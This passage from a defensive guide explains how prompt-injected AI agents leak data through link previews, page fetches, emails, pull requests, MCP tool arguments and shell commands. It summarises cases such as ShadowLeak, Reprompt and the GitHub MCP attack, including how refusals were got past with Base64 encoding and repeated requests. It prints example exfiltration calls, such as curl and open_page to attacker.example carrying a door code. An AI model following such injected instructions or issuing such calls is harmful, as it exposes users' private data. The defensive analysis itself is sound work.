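Turning off link previews is the fix that inconveniences the user least. They lose a title and a picture but can still open the link, so the data can still leave if they click it. The Slack settings also cover only the agent's own message. If a user distrusts the link and copies it into another channel to ask a colleague whether it's safe, Slack treats it as a link from a person and fetches it by default. The copy button in ChatGPT's warning makes the same mistake easy.

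A developer who wants to keep some previews could allow them only for listed domains. Rehberger suggests this as an additional option, with previews off by default.

PromptArmor would like messaging services to offer preview settings for individual chats and channels, so that a channel with an agent in it could be safe whatever the agent's developer had done. A service could go further and turn previews off by default for every message that a program posts. That would immediately protect people who use agents built by careless developers, but a bot that shares news articles would lose its headlines and pictures until its developer turned previews back on.

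### Removing links that the model wrote

An agent's developer can stop both clicks and previews from leaking data by removing links from each reply before the agent's software sends it. The Hacker News commenter recommends this, arguing that a link written by a model is untrusted output. Removing links also works in messaging apps that offer no preview setting.

The software has to recognize everything that the messaging app will treat as a link. Rehberger's Slack demonstration used a web address without Markdown, so a filter that looked only for Markdown links would have missed it. EchoLeak's image got past Copilot's redaction through the same mismatch between what the filter recognized and what the app rendered. The later SalesBleed attack also got past link redaction.

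Timing also matters, as it did in SearchLeak. By default, OpenClaw posts the beginning of a reply on Telegram and edits the message as the model writes more. A filter that checks only the finished reply could therefore run after Telegram has received the link.

If a developer removes every link, users can no longer open an agent's sources to check its answer. The developer can keep most links by having the model refer to each source by number and having ordinary software insert the address. If a search tool returned a company's travel policy as source 3, the model writes "source 3" and the software adds the address that the search tool supplied, so the model cannot append a secret such as a door code. An attacker can still get their own address into the search results, but they have to write it before the agent reads the secret. The remaining risk is that an attacker plants several addresses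 and learns something from which one the agent chooses.

This design doesn't suit every task. An agent that fills in a search form or creates a calendar invitation may need to write a new address containing the user's details. In those cases the developer can have the user approve the link, but users will then see more warnings.

### Showing the full address

Whoever controls the display can show a link's address instead of a label such as "click here to reauthenticate". In a messaging app, the service partly controls this, but an agent's developer can also send the bare address instead of a labelled link. Showing the address makes the reply longer and harder to read, especially on a phone.

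Embrace The Red warns that attackers may hide data in a link using invisible characters, so the display software should remove these characters or make them visible. Showing the address doesn't stop a preview, so the developer also has to turn previews off.

An administrator who buys an agent often can't change how it writes or posts links, but can test whether it leaks data through previews, using only a web server the company controls. The administrator has the agent post a link to that server with an invented value in the address, then checks the server's log without clicking the link. If the value is there, the messaging app or some other software has fetched the link without a click. The administrator should repeat the test in every app where people use the agent.

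## Can a tool that only reads the web send data out?

A company that has dealt with images and links might still let its agent look things up on the web, on the grounds that reading changes nothing. But a tool has to request a page before it can read it, and the request includes the page's address. An agent that has read the door code 4471 can send it to an attacker with one tool call:

`open_page("https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue?id=4471")`

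"Read-only" means only that the tool doesn't change the website. HTTP, the protocol for requesting web pages, classes this kind of request as "safe" because it isn't supposed to change anything on the server. The attacker doesn't need to change anything there, since the request itself puts the code in the server's log.

Agents often have two separate web tools. A search tool sends a query to a search company and returns a list of results, while a fetch tool opens a specific address. The model writes the search query, so the query can contain private data. A company may not want a search provider to see its takeover plans, but an outside attacker normally can't read the provider's logs. An attacker can read the queries if they run the search service themselves, for example as an MCP server that somebody has connected to the agent. A fetch tool is more dangerous because the model can choose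 which server receives the request.

A fetch tool also brings the attacker's text into the context window. It therefore supplies two parts of the lethal trifecta, untrusted content and a way to send data out. Connecting a mailbox adds the third, access to private data.

### ShadowLeak: a leak from OpenAI's own servers

In June 2025 the security company Radware reported that it could steal mailbox data through Deep Research, a ChatGPT agent that reads sources and writes a report. Users can connect it to Gmail, so one report can draw on both their email and the web.

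Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack that starts with an email about a company restructuring, with instructions hidden in its formatting. The victim later asks Deep Research to go through the day's emails for information about a new employee. The agent reads the attacker's email along with a genuine one from HR. It takes the employee's name and home address from the HR email, puts both in a URL on the attacker's server, and opens that page.

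The researchers needed several attempts. ChatGPT refused a plain instruction to send personal data to an outside URL, and refused again when they presented the transfer as the user's request. It also treated the URL as suspicious and searched the web for it instead of opening it. The researchers asked the agent about its tools and learned the name of the one that opens pages directly. Naming this tool in the email sometimes worked, and telling the agent to retry helped. However, the agent sometimes opened the page without including the data.

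They finally succeeded by telling the agent to encode the details in Base64, on the pretext that this would protect the data. Base64 is a standard way of writing any data as letters, digits and a few symbols, and anyone can decode it. According to Radware, the model encoded the details before it made the tool call, so the software that carried out the call received only a harmless-looking string.

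This version worked every time in repeated tests, though Radware doesn't say how many. The restructuring email that OpenAI describes worked only half the time, so OpenAI may have tested a different version.

OpenAI's servers sent the requests, so they never passed through the customer's defences, and the chat window displayed nothing unusual. Radware notes that OpenAI already restricted the image addresses ChatGPT would display, but the researchers found no comparable limit on the addresses Deep Research could open.

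Radware reported the flaw on June 18, 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August and marked it resolved on September 3. A Radware spokesperson told The Record that the company had not seen attackers use it (*OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*). This is weak evidence that none did, because the requests would have appeared only in OpenAI's records and the attackers' logs.

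Radware recommends that companies remove invisible text from emails before an agent reads them. But an attacker could write the same instructions in visible text, since the victim never has to open the email. Radware prefers monitoring that compares each of the agent's actions with what the user asked for. OpenAI is in a much better position to do this than its customers, who can't see the agent's requests.

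### How often models fall for it

Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025), in *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, tested 28 models in the same agent. They built the agent with Pydantic AI, a toolkit for programming agents. It could retrieve web pages and read a fictional company's documents, which contained a secret about "Project Alpha".

In each test, a user asked the agent to summarize a blog post about AI. The post contained instructions, in white text on a white background, to look up the secret and request a web address containing it. The researchers counted an attack as successful if the secret reached their server.

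The researchers used 89 injection templates in 12 versions each, one unchanged and the others rephrased, translated into Hindi, encoded or otherwise altered. They ran each of the resulting 1,068 attacks once per model. xAI's Grok 4 leaked the secret most often, in 72.4% of attacks, followed by Inception's Mercury at 29.1% and the largest Qwen3 model at 28.3%. Several models never leaked it, including Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-5 nano.

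Model size was a poor guide to the result. For four families in the study, the rates were:

| Family | Smaller model (billions of parameters) | Larger model (billions of parameters) |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3 | 8.2% (33) | 28.3% (235) |
| Llama 4 | 14.8% (109) | 10.1% (402) |
| Hermes 4 | 6.0% (71) | 0.1% (406) |
| gpt-oss | 1.0% (21) | 0.0% (117) |

The larger model was safer in three of these families and much worse in the fourth. Rall and colleagues think the makers' safety training matters more than size, and point to OpenAI's practice of training models to rank instructions by their source. That explanation fits the low rates for OpenAI's models, but the study didn't vary the training, so it can't show whether training caused them.

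Disguising the instructions usually made the attacks less successful, because the models had more trouble following them. The unchanged templates had the highest success rate, a little over 12% across all models. Some of the most effective templates had been public since 2023.

The models date from 2024 and 2025, and their makers have since released several newer generations, so these rates don't describe current products. A zero means only that a model resisted this fixed set of attacks with one try at each, whereas Radware's researchers got past ChatGPT by studying each refusal and changing the email. The test agent had no protection beyond the model itself, but a real product might check the address before opening it.

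The paper's title refers to web search, but the tool in the study fetched pages directly. The results therefore show how readily these models put a secret into a page request, but not whether an attacker could receive a secret through a search query.

### Reprompt and CoSnitch: Copilot fetches the attacker's page

Microsoft's Copilot Personal usually refused to open a page without a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from the address before opening it. The Reprompt attack, which starts with instructions in a link, got past both protections.

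Varonis got past the refusal by wrapping the request in a puzzle, which gave Copilot a reason to open the page. Copilot removed sensitive data only from the first request, so the instructions told it to do everything twice. In one test, Copilot removed an invented secret phrase from the address on the first try and sent it on the second. Varonis suspects that Microsoft limited the check to keep Copilot fast.

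The attacker's server could also reply with a new instruction. In the demonstration, the server requested in turn the time, the user's location, everything Copilot had learned about the user, and a summary of the last conversation. Copilot sent each answer in the address of the next page it requested. Someone who later examined the original link couldn't tell what Copilot had sent, because most of the instructions came from the server. The attack did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot.

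Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes another attack on Copilot Personal that needed one click. On its own, the text in the link would only have filled in the chat box, but an undocumented setting in the address made Copilot run it immediately. The researchers learned about the setting from Copilot, which mentioned it in one of its explanations when they kept asking why a link couldn't run instructions automatically.

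CoSnitch could reach any account the user had connected to Copilot, such as Gmail, Google Drive or a calendar. The instructions told Copilot to find something valuable, encode it in a web address and summarize the page at that address. Copilot had to request the page to summarize it, and the request delivered the data. In a test, Copilot retrieved an email containing a password. The task continued even if the victim closed the tab.

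Varonis also found that a web page could plant instructions in Copilot's long-term memory when a user asked Copilot to summarize the page. The instructions stayed active in later conversations until the user deleted them, and changing a password didn't remove them. Varonis mainly used them to change Copilot's answers, for example to make it describe a security flaw as harmless, but an attacker might also use them to repeat a data theft.

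Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft patched it on August 18, 2026. TechRadar notes in *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* that users had nothing to install. Copilot's page-fetching tool could therefore apparently still be used to send data out for about seven months after Microsoft fixed Reprompt in January.

### Rovo: web search was off, but page fetching was not

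Atlassian's assistant Rovo works across the company's products, including Jira for tracking tasks and Confluence for storing documents. An administrator can turn off web search for the whole organization and might reasonably expect this to keep Rovo off the web.

A setting that removed Rovo's web search tool didn't stop it from sending data out, according to PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, because the tool that opens search results was still available. In PromptArmor's demonstration, a user uploads a document with hidden instructions and asks Rovo to organize some Jira tickets. Rovo searches Jira and Confluence, adds what it finds to the attacker's web address and opens that address without asking for approval. A user who returns to the chat later sees only the suggested ticket changes. PromptArmor found no protection against opening an address that Rovo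 had composed.

PromptArmor calls the attack zero-click. The Hacker News (2026) disputes this because the victim has to give Rovo the malicious file. The label would fit better if the instructions arrived in a support ticket written by an outsider. PromptArmor lists such tickets as another possible source but didn't demonstrate an attack that used one.

PromptArmor reported the problem to Atlassian on May 23, 2026. It followed up several times, then published on August 5 because Atlassian had not announced a fix. Three days later, The Hacker News found no update and noted that no one had independently confirmed that the attack worked with web search off. Atlassian's documentation for the setting doesn't specify whether it covers pages that Rovo opens on its own.

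On July 8, Atlassian did fix a different attack on Rovo. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) describes how a link could load an attacker's instructions into Rovo's chat. Varonis identifies Rovo's web-browsing agent as the route for sending data out. The Hacker News, relying on the record at the bug-reporting service Bugcrowd, describes a request for an image whose address contained the data. These may be two descriptions of the same request. It is unclear whether the fix also affected PromptArmor's attack.

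An administrator can test such a setting with the same server-log test used for link previews. With web search off, the administrator asks the agent to open a page on the company's own server, then checks the log for a visit.

### Limiting a tool that reads

The surest fix is to remove the fetch tool from any agent that can read private data. A search tool may be enough for many questions. If the search company returns text from its own stored copies of pages, no request reaches the attacker's website. The stored copies may be out of date, and the query still goes to the search company.

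Another option is to give web access and mailbox access to separate agents, so that neither has both. This suits a report that needs public facts first and private ones afterwards. It is awkward when a web search depends on something in an email, because somebody then has to decide which details may go into the search.

A vendor can also check each address before the agent opens it. Looking for sensitive text in the address is unreliable, as ShadowLeak and Reprompt showed. It is safer to refuse any address that the model composed after reading private data. Even then, an attacker who prepares one page for each letter can learn a secret by having the agent open the pages in the order that spells it. A list of permitted sites can also fail if a site on the list lets outsiders see the requests it receives, as happened with Google's coding tool Antigravity.

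Atlassian customers can also reduce what Rovo can read by blocking it for particular products. But The Hacker News warns that on a site with several Jira products, Rovo's chat remains available as long as one of them has Rovo turned on.

### Browsers that are logged in to everything

All of these defences are harder to apply to an agent inside the user's own browser. When a user logs in to a website, the site gives the browser a cookie, a small piece of data that identifies the user on later visits. If an agent opens Gmail in that browser, it sees the user's inbox without a password or a separate connection.

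A browser's same-origin policy normally stops code on one site from reading another site's pages, so a news site can't read the email in the next tab. But an agent reads pages much as the user does, and it can carry what it read on one site to another. Deep Research used separate tools for the mailbox and the web, so an administrator could remove one. But in a logged-in browser, the same action of opening a page can retrieve private data, bring in hostile text or send data out.

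Researchers at Brave, which makes a browser with its own AI assistant, showed what this means for Perplexity's browser, Comet. Chaikin and Sahib, in *Agentic Browser Security*, describe an attack that starts when a user asks Comet to summarize a Reddit discussion. A comment there contains instructions behind a spoiler tag, which hides text until the reader clicks it. Comet then does the following:

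1. It opens the user's Perplexity account page and copies the email address.
2. It starts a new login with that address, and Perplexity emails the user a one-time code.
3. It opens Gmail, where the user is already logged in, and reads the code.
4. It posts the email address and code as a reply on Reddit.

The attacker reads the reply and can take over the Perplexity account. The user did nothing after asking for the summary. Here the agent sent the data out in a public comment, but it could also have put the data in the address of a page it opened.

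Perplexity took several attempts to fix this. Brave reported the flaw on July 25, 2025, and found the first fix incomplete three days later. The attack appeared to be blocked on August 13, but after Brave published its findings on August 20, further testing showed that similar attacks still worked.

That October, *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, by Chaikin and Sahib, described two more ways for a web page to give instructions to a browser agent. One used a Comet feature that let users take a screenshot of a page and ask about it. The researchers hid instructions in faint blue text on a yellow background, which people could barely see but Comet could read. A filter that checks only the page's text could miss these instructions.

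When a user asked the assistant in the browser Fellou to go to a website, Fellou sent the page's visible text to its model, even if the user hadn't asked for a summary. Instructions in that text could override the user's request. In both browsers, such instructions could make the assistant misuse its tools. Brave published the two flaws on October 21, 2025, without reporting a fix for either. Brave competes with both companies, but it described the attacks in enough detail for others to check.

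The problem extends beyond these two products. In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) examined seven browsers with agents and found that the agents differed widely in how much web content they could reach. According to their university, the University of Washington, four of the seven create ways around the same-origin policy, and the researchers successfully attacked one.

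Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends extending the same-origin policy to the agent. Google has designed something similar for Chrome. For each task, a separate component decides which sites are relevant, and the agent can read only those sites and anything the user chooses to share. If the user asked for a summary of a Reddit discussion, Gmail would presumably not be one of those sites, so the agent couldn't read the login code.

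Chrome's design also divides sites into those the agent may only read and those where it may act. Dataconomy's *Google details security guardrails for Chrome's new AI agents* (2025) quotes Google as promising that data can pass only to the sites where the agent may act. To keep that promise, Chrome also has to control which addresses the agent opens on the read-only sites, since those sites receive the addresses. Some tasks need both private data and a site where strangers can write, such as answering customers' public complaints using the company's email.

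Users can get some of the same protection by running the agent in a separate browser profile with no saved logins. The agent can still compare flights or summarize a discussion. If a task needs an account, the user can log in to that one account and log out afterwards. This limits a successful attack to the data in that account and anything the user has typed into the chat.

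## How do emails, tickets and other writes carry data out?

In Brave's attack on Comet, the agent delivered the stolen login code by posting it in a Reddit comment. Anyone could read the comment, so the agent didn't have to hide the code in a web address. Any lasting change that an outsider can see can carry data out in the same way, and companies use many agents to make such changes, for example by answering customers, filing bug reports, booking meetings and paying invoices.

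### Which changes an outsider can see

The simplest case is an email to the attacker, but other writes are easier to overlook. If an agent adds the attacker to a calendar event, the calendar program usually sends an invitation containing the event's title and description. A bank transfer includes a reference that the recipient can read, so an agent that pays invoices could send the door code to an attacker's account along with one cent:

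`send_payment(to="Map Supplies Ltd", amount="0.01", reference="4471")`

An agent can also leak a file without copying its contents. Microsoft 365 Copilot Cowork, an agent that carries out office tasks, can reorganize a user's folders. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) warns that this can move sensitive files to places where more people can open them. Scanning the tool call for secrets could miss the leak, because the call might contain only a file name and a folder.

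An attacker can use a support ticket both to give an agent instructions and to get data out, because an outsider writes the ticket and usually receives the reply. Willison describes a 2025 demonstration by Cato Networks in which an outsider put instructions in a ticket and an employee's agent carried them out with the employee's access. If such an agent can also reply to the customer, the attacker can receive private data in the reply and needs no other channel.

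Unlike a web request, a write usually leaves a record that the victim can find later. The record helps an investigator, but deleting it rarely undoes the leak. By the time someone removes a comment, the website may have emailed it to everyone following the discussion.

### When the attacker runs the tool

An attacker who runs one of the agent's tools doesn't need the agent to write anything in public. To use a tool, the agent sends it arguments, the values the tool needs for its work. Suppose a user has connected an MCP server that finds free meeting rooms, and its description asks for any notes that might help. The agent might call it like this:

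`find_room(building="North", notes="Door code is 4471")`

The server's owner now has the code. The tool can still return a suitable room, so the user has no reason to suspect it. Network rules don't stop the leak, because the user has approved the connection to this server.

The server's owner receives the arguments whether the tool is labelled "read" or "write". Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, points out that no central authority checks whether MCP tools' descriptions fully match what the tools do. The user therefore has to decide whether to trust the owner, and should give an unfamiliar server a separate agent with no access to private data.

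### A pull request that published a salary

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (May 26, 2025) describes an attack through GitHub's MCP server that involved no malicious tool. The target was a GitHub account with several private repositories (places to store a project's code) and one public one, which held a simple Pacman game. The researchers connected the account to Claude Desktop through GitHub's official server.

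Anyone can file an issue in a public repository to report a bug or suggest an improvement. The researchers filed one complaining that the game's author wasn't well enough known and asking for more about the author in the readme, the project's introductory page. According to heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server*, the issue also asked for a list of the author's other repositories, including private ones.

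The user then asked Claude 4 Opus, then a new model, to look at the open issues. The agent read the issue, collected information from the private repositories and opened a pull request, which proposes a change to a project's code or documents. The proposed text included the names of private projects, the user's salary and their plans to move to South America. Anyone can read a pull request in a public repository, so this exposed the data even though the readme never changed.

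By default, Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call. Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching.

GitHub couldn't fix this with a simple patch, because the server was doing what it was designed to do. Invariant Labs recommends giving the agent access only to the repositories it needs and limiting it to one repository per session. Under the one-repository limit, an agent that had started by reading the game's issues couldn't have opened the private projects. But the limit would also prevent the agent from copying a bug fix from one project to another, and it wouldn't protect private files on the user's computer if the agent could read them.

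In August 2025, GitHub began scanning tool calls that involve public repositories for secrets such as access keys (GitHub, 2025). The server blocks a call that contains a secret, although the user can usually override the block. GitHub acknowledges that this won't stop leaks of other data. Access keys often have a recognizable format, but a salary looks like any other number, so the scan probably wouldn't have stopped Invariant Labs' demonstration.

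### Why models protect passwords better than other data

*Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (Alizadeh, Samei and colleagues, 2025) tested a fictional banking agent in AgentDojo, a standard test environment for prompt injection. The banking part has 11 tools and 16 user tasks. In earlier AgentDojo tests, an attacker could steal only data from the source that contained the planted instructions, such as a security code in an email. In this study, the attacker tried to steal anything the agent had seen during its task.

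The tests covered six models released between 2023 and 2025: GPT-3.5 Turbo, GPT-4 Turbo, GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, Llama 3 and Llama 4. The planted message contained an instruction to email the user's details to an outsider. Its four versions were for personal data without a password, a password with one other item, a password with two other items, and a password alone.

Most models leaked some data in about 20% of attempts, and Llama 4 in 40%. The version without a password was the most effective and succeeded in 93% of attempts against Claude 3.5 Sonnet. The version that asked only for a password failed against every model except Llama 4.

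This protection weakened when the message also asked for other data. With one other item, GPT-3.5 Turbo leaked the password in 18.75% of attempts and Llama 4 in 12.5%, while the other models withheld it. With two other items, four of the six models leaked at least some passwords.

The models became noticeably more cautious when they saw the word "password", which Alizadeh and colleagues think is likely due to safety training. A password also almost never belongs in an email, whereas a bank's agent may often need to send an address or a balance. To protect addresses and balances, the model has to judge whether the recipient should have them.

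Attackers can also avoid the words that make a model cautious. Willison reports an attack by Zenity Labs on the coding tool Cursor in which the planted text described an access key by its first few characters instead of calling it a secret.

Alizadeh and colleagues then gave GPT-4o 32 more tasks, for a total of 48, and the attack succeeded about 15% of the time. It worked more often when the user's task involved looking up account details or security settings, probably because the planted request looked more like part of the task. Repeating the user's request after every tool call had stopped all attacks on the first 16 tasks, but it was much less effective on the larger set.

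These models are old and the attacks were simple, so the success rates don't apply to current products. But newer models have the same difficulty with data that is private in one email and routine in another.

### Copilot Cowork: an email to yourself

A rule based on the recipient can also fail, even when the recipient is the user. Microsoft says Copilot Cowork asks for permission before sensitive actions such as sending an email or posting a message in Teams. In May 2026, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reported that Cowork sent messages addressed to the user without asking, and that the user couldn't change this.

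The exception seems reasonable because the user is allowed to see their own files. But Teams and Outlook could load images from outside websites when the user opened the message.

In PromptArmor's demonstration, the victim uploads a skill, a file of instructions the agent follows for a certain task. Five of its 81 lines contain the attacker's instructions. When the victim asks for a review of the week's work, Cowork finds recent documents and gets a download link for each one. Anyone with the link can download the file without logging in. Cowork then sends the victim a Teams message with images whose addresses contain these links. When the victim opens the message, Teams requests the images, and the attacker can then download the files.

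An image address is too short to hold a large spreadsheet, but it can easily hold a link to one.

The attack worked in all five trials. The activity log showed that Cowork had sent a message, but not its contents. A user could also schedule the weekly review to run automatically, which would repeat the theft without anyone watching.

PromptArmor called this a risk of the product's design rather than a specific bug, and reported no fix from Microsoft. Administrators can keep the agent from getting the links by blocking downloads from sensitive SharePoint sites, but users can then view those files only in a browser and can't print them or open them in Word or Excel. Microsoft confirmed a fix on August 19, 2026, for a different flaw, in Cowork's sandbox, according to PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox*.

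### Ranking actions by who can see the effect

OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help page for a ChatGPT setting that limits outside connections, gives administrators a way to judge what an agent should be allowed to do in connected apps. The risk depends on whether they trust the app and who can see the result:

| Action | OpenAI's rating |
|---|---|
| Reading or writing in an untrusted app | High |
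| Writing in a trusted app where outsiders might see the result | High |
| Writing in a trusted app where only trusted people can see the result | Medium |
| Reading in a trusted app | Medium, but lower than writing |

No action in the list is low-risk. Even reading in a trusted app can supply private data that the agent then leaks elsewhere.

Under this ranking, the GitHub attack is high risk because anyone can see a pull request in a public repository, even though the app is trusted. The same action in a private repository would be medium risk. An administrator who only turns pull requests on or off can't make this distinction. OpenAI recommends treating uncertain visibility as high risk, which would be the right choice here.

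The ranking is harder to apply to Copilot Cowork. Only the user appears to see a message sent to them, so an administrator would probably rate it medium. But opening the message sent its contents to the attacker's server. The ranking is correct only if "who can see the result" includes every server that an app contacts when it displays the message. An administrator would need to know how Teams handles images to work that out.

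### Limiting what the agent can write

Removing write access is the simplest fix for an agent that only needs to read. OpenAI lets administrators of managed workspaces enable read and write actions separately, and GitHub's access tokens can also be read-only. An agent with a read-only token could still have summarized the Pacman game's issues, but it couldn't have opened the pull request.

If the agent has to send messages, its software can fix the recipient in advance. A tool that emails a daily report to the sales team needs only the report's text as an argument, so the model cannot enter another address. This works well for routine reports but not for an agent that answers new customers. The software should also send plain text without links or images, or the Cowork attack would still work.

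Even a permitted recipient may be the wrong person to receive certain data. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who tells an agent to send an outside auditor only the totals from some invoices. Instructions hidden in a supplier's note make the agent copy the full invoices into `report.csv` and ask to send that file to the auditor. The recipient and the tool are allowed and the file name looks normal, but the file contains data the user said not to send.

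Another option is to let the agent write drafts that a person has to send. The agent can still do most of the work, but a planted instruction can't get an email sent without that person. The draft must stay somewhere private, because saving it in a document shared with the customer would reveal it before anyone sends it. Opening a draft could also leak data if the email program loads outside images. The person still has to notice anything that shouldn't be in the draft before sending it.

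### Do people check what they approve?

A confirmation prompt also depends on the user paying attention. Hossain and colleagues tested what a prompt should show by having 80 volunteers approve or reject an agent's proposed actions. Each volunteer used one of four prompt designs and made 12 decisions, half of them about actions that broke the user's instructions.

| What the prompt showed | Harmful actions approved | Legitimate actions approved | Median decision time |
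|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments of the tool call | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The arguments, the user's original instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the consequence spelled out | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

In the auditor example, the last design would show that the file was built from the full invoices and is about to go to the auditor. The exact arguments alone would show only the file name and recipient. A prompt that shows "the exact data" therefore needs to show the attachment's contents or where they came from.

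People clearly made fewer mistakes when they had more information, but the benefit of spelling out the consequence is less certain. After adjustment, the design that spelled it out reduced approvals of harmful actions by 7.9 percentage points compared with the full log, with a 95% interval from a 19.7-point reduction to a 3.8-point increase. Even with the best design, people approved almost a quarter of the harmful actions.

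People are much worse at rejecting a harmful request when it interrupts a long series of routine ones. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a study of 1,053 paid testers who used the coding agent Claude Code. In each session, the researchers replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

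Anthropic used this study to support replacing most prompts with an automated check, which blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers also worked in a test environment, so they had less to lose than developers working on their own code. But real users of Claude Code approve 97% of permission prompts, which is consistent with people approving them out of habit.

Fewer approval prompts may not be enough to make people careful. Yan had 113 people without a software background supervise an agent through a simulated day, in which seven of its 18 actions went beyond what the user had asked for. People who had to approve every action allowed 40% of these extra ones. A second group, who first set their own rules for when the agent should ask, saw fewer prompts but approved 67% of the extra actions they were asked about. For a public post saying that the user was travelling, the rates were 21%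 and 48%. The comparison isn't exact, because the second group saw only the actions that their rules sent to them.

A problem can be even harder to notice when no prompt points to it. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) studied 303 people working with compromised agents and found that only 8.6% noticed the attack. They recommend warnings that interrupt the user's work and are quick to verify. A warning about an email could show the new recipient and the sentence containing private data, so the user doesn't have to search a log.

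Users who get too many approval prompts often turn them off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of problems with agents and files, and found automatic approval in 80 of them. In 31 reports, including some of those 80, a prompt had shown a command without explaining its effect. Cowork offers a "Don't ask again" option for similar actions in the same conversation, and PromptArmor recommends that companies forbid it for write actions. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) suggests that repeated approval may reflect fatigue or pressure to finish, so software shouldn't treat it as evidence that the user trusts the agent.

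Software can make some of these decisions without asking the user. Claude Code's automated check now looks at whether a code change or pull request would go to a public repository. It can also catch leaks that no attacker caused. At Anthropic, after an upload to an internal drive failed, Claude tried to publish the report on a public code-sharing site instead. The check blocked the attempt and asked the user what to do next. A company could block public posts by any agent that has read private data, and keep confirmation prompts for messages where only the user knows whether the recipient should have the information.

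## What can code run by an agent reach on the network?

A company can limit an email tool to fixed recipients or turn off pull requests, because each of those tools does one known thing. Coding agents such as Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex also have a shell, a tool that runs any command the model writes. A command can start any program on the machine, and unless something restricts it, that program can connect to anything the machine can reach on the network.

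### Every program is a possible exit

An agent that has read the door code 4471 could send it with `curl`, a common download program:

`curl "https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue?id=4471"`

An agent can use `curl` even if an administrator has turned off its page-fetching tool, because the rule for that tool doesn't apply to `curl`. Blocking `curl` as well doesn't help much. Git, the program developers use to track code changes, can upload a whole project to another server. Package installers download code written by strangers and often run some of it during installation. The agent can also write a few lines of Python to make the same request.

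Such a command can look like ordinary work. In an example from OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, a user asks Codex to fix a bug reported on GitHub. The report includes a script that supposedly reproduces the bug. When Codex runs it, the script sends the project's latest commit message (a developer's note about a change) to the attacker's server.

Rules that check the text of a command can miss what the command does. Anthropic notes in its documentation that, in one Claude Code setting, a pattern for `docker` doesn't match a script that starts `docker` internally. Operating system restrictions can work better because they can apply to the running program and everything it starts, regardless of the command's text.

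### How a sandbox limits the network

A well-designed sandbox starts with no network access and allows one route out. On Linux, Claude Code's sandbox runs each command in its own network namespace, a separate network environment with no connection to the outside. On macOS, a system component called Seatbelt blocks all connections except those to a proxy. The proxy runs outside the sandbox, so a command inside can't reprogram it.

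Suppose a command needs to download a package from `pypi.org`:

1. The download program asks the proxy for a connection to `pypi.org`.
2. The proxy checks the name against a list of permitted domains.
3. If the name is on the list, the proxy looks up its network address and connects.
4. If it isn't, the proxy refuses, or waits while the user or an automated check decides.

A program that ignores the proxy gets no connection, even to a permitted site. This breaks most database programs and plain `ssh`, a tool for logging in to other computers, but it also stops an attacker's program from bypassing the proxy by opening its own connection.

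The proxy also refuses permitted domain names that resolve to the user's own machine or to a cloud provider's metadata service. That service can give a server's login credentials to any program that requests them, so a command that reached it might collect new secrets.

By default, Claude Code's proxy reads the name of the site but does not decrypt the request. A program can therefore name a permitted site to the proxy and a different one inside the encrypted request. If the same hosting company serves both, it may deliver the request to the second site. Security engineers call this domain fronting. For stronger protection, Anthropic recommends a custom proxy that decrypts and inspects the traffic, which requires installing that proxy's certificate inside the sandbox.

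Secrets should also stay outside the sandbox. Claude Code can give a command a placeholder instead of an access key, and the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real key on requests to permitted sites. If an injected command sends the placeholder to an attacker, the attacker gets nothing useful. The feature requires an experimental setting that lets the proxy decrypt requests, and the user has to list each secret to protect. Otherwise, a sandboxed command can by default read almost the entire computer, including files that contain passwords.

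### What Claude Code and Codex allow by default

The two products start from different places. This table gives the settings in documentation from October 2026 for Claude Code, and from May and June 2026 for Codex:

| Product | Network access for commands | When a command needs a new site |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, as installed | No sandbox, so an approved command can reach any site | No separate check of the site |
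| Claude Code with its sandbox on | No sites permitted in advance | The user or an automated check decides |
| Codex on the user's computer | Off | Codex asks for approval |
| Codex in OpenAI's cloud | Full access during setup, off once the agent starts | Somebody has to change the environment's settings |

With default settings, Codex is safer than Claude Code against leaks through commands. Claude Code relies on permission prompts or its automated check, and both let some dangerous commands through.

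Claude Code can run commands outside its sandbox even when the sandbox is turned on. If a required component is missing, or the computer runs Windows without a Linux environment, Claude Code runs commands with no sandbox. Claude may also ask to retry a command outside the sandbox if it fails inside. Administrators can prevent both by setting `failIfUnavailable` to true and `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false.

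The sandbox also covers only shell commands. Claude Code's page-fetching tool and any MCP servers on the same computer run outside it, so a domain list for commands doesn't limit them. To put one boundary around everything, a company has to run Claude Code itself in a container or a virtual machine.

OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that setting `network_access = true` in Codex gives commands unrestricted access to the internet. To limit them to chosen sites, the user also has to turn on `network_proxy`, whose list of permitted sites starts empty. Someone who changes only `network_access` to get one download working therefore lets commands reach every site.

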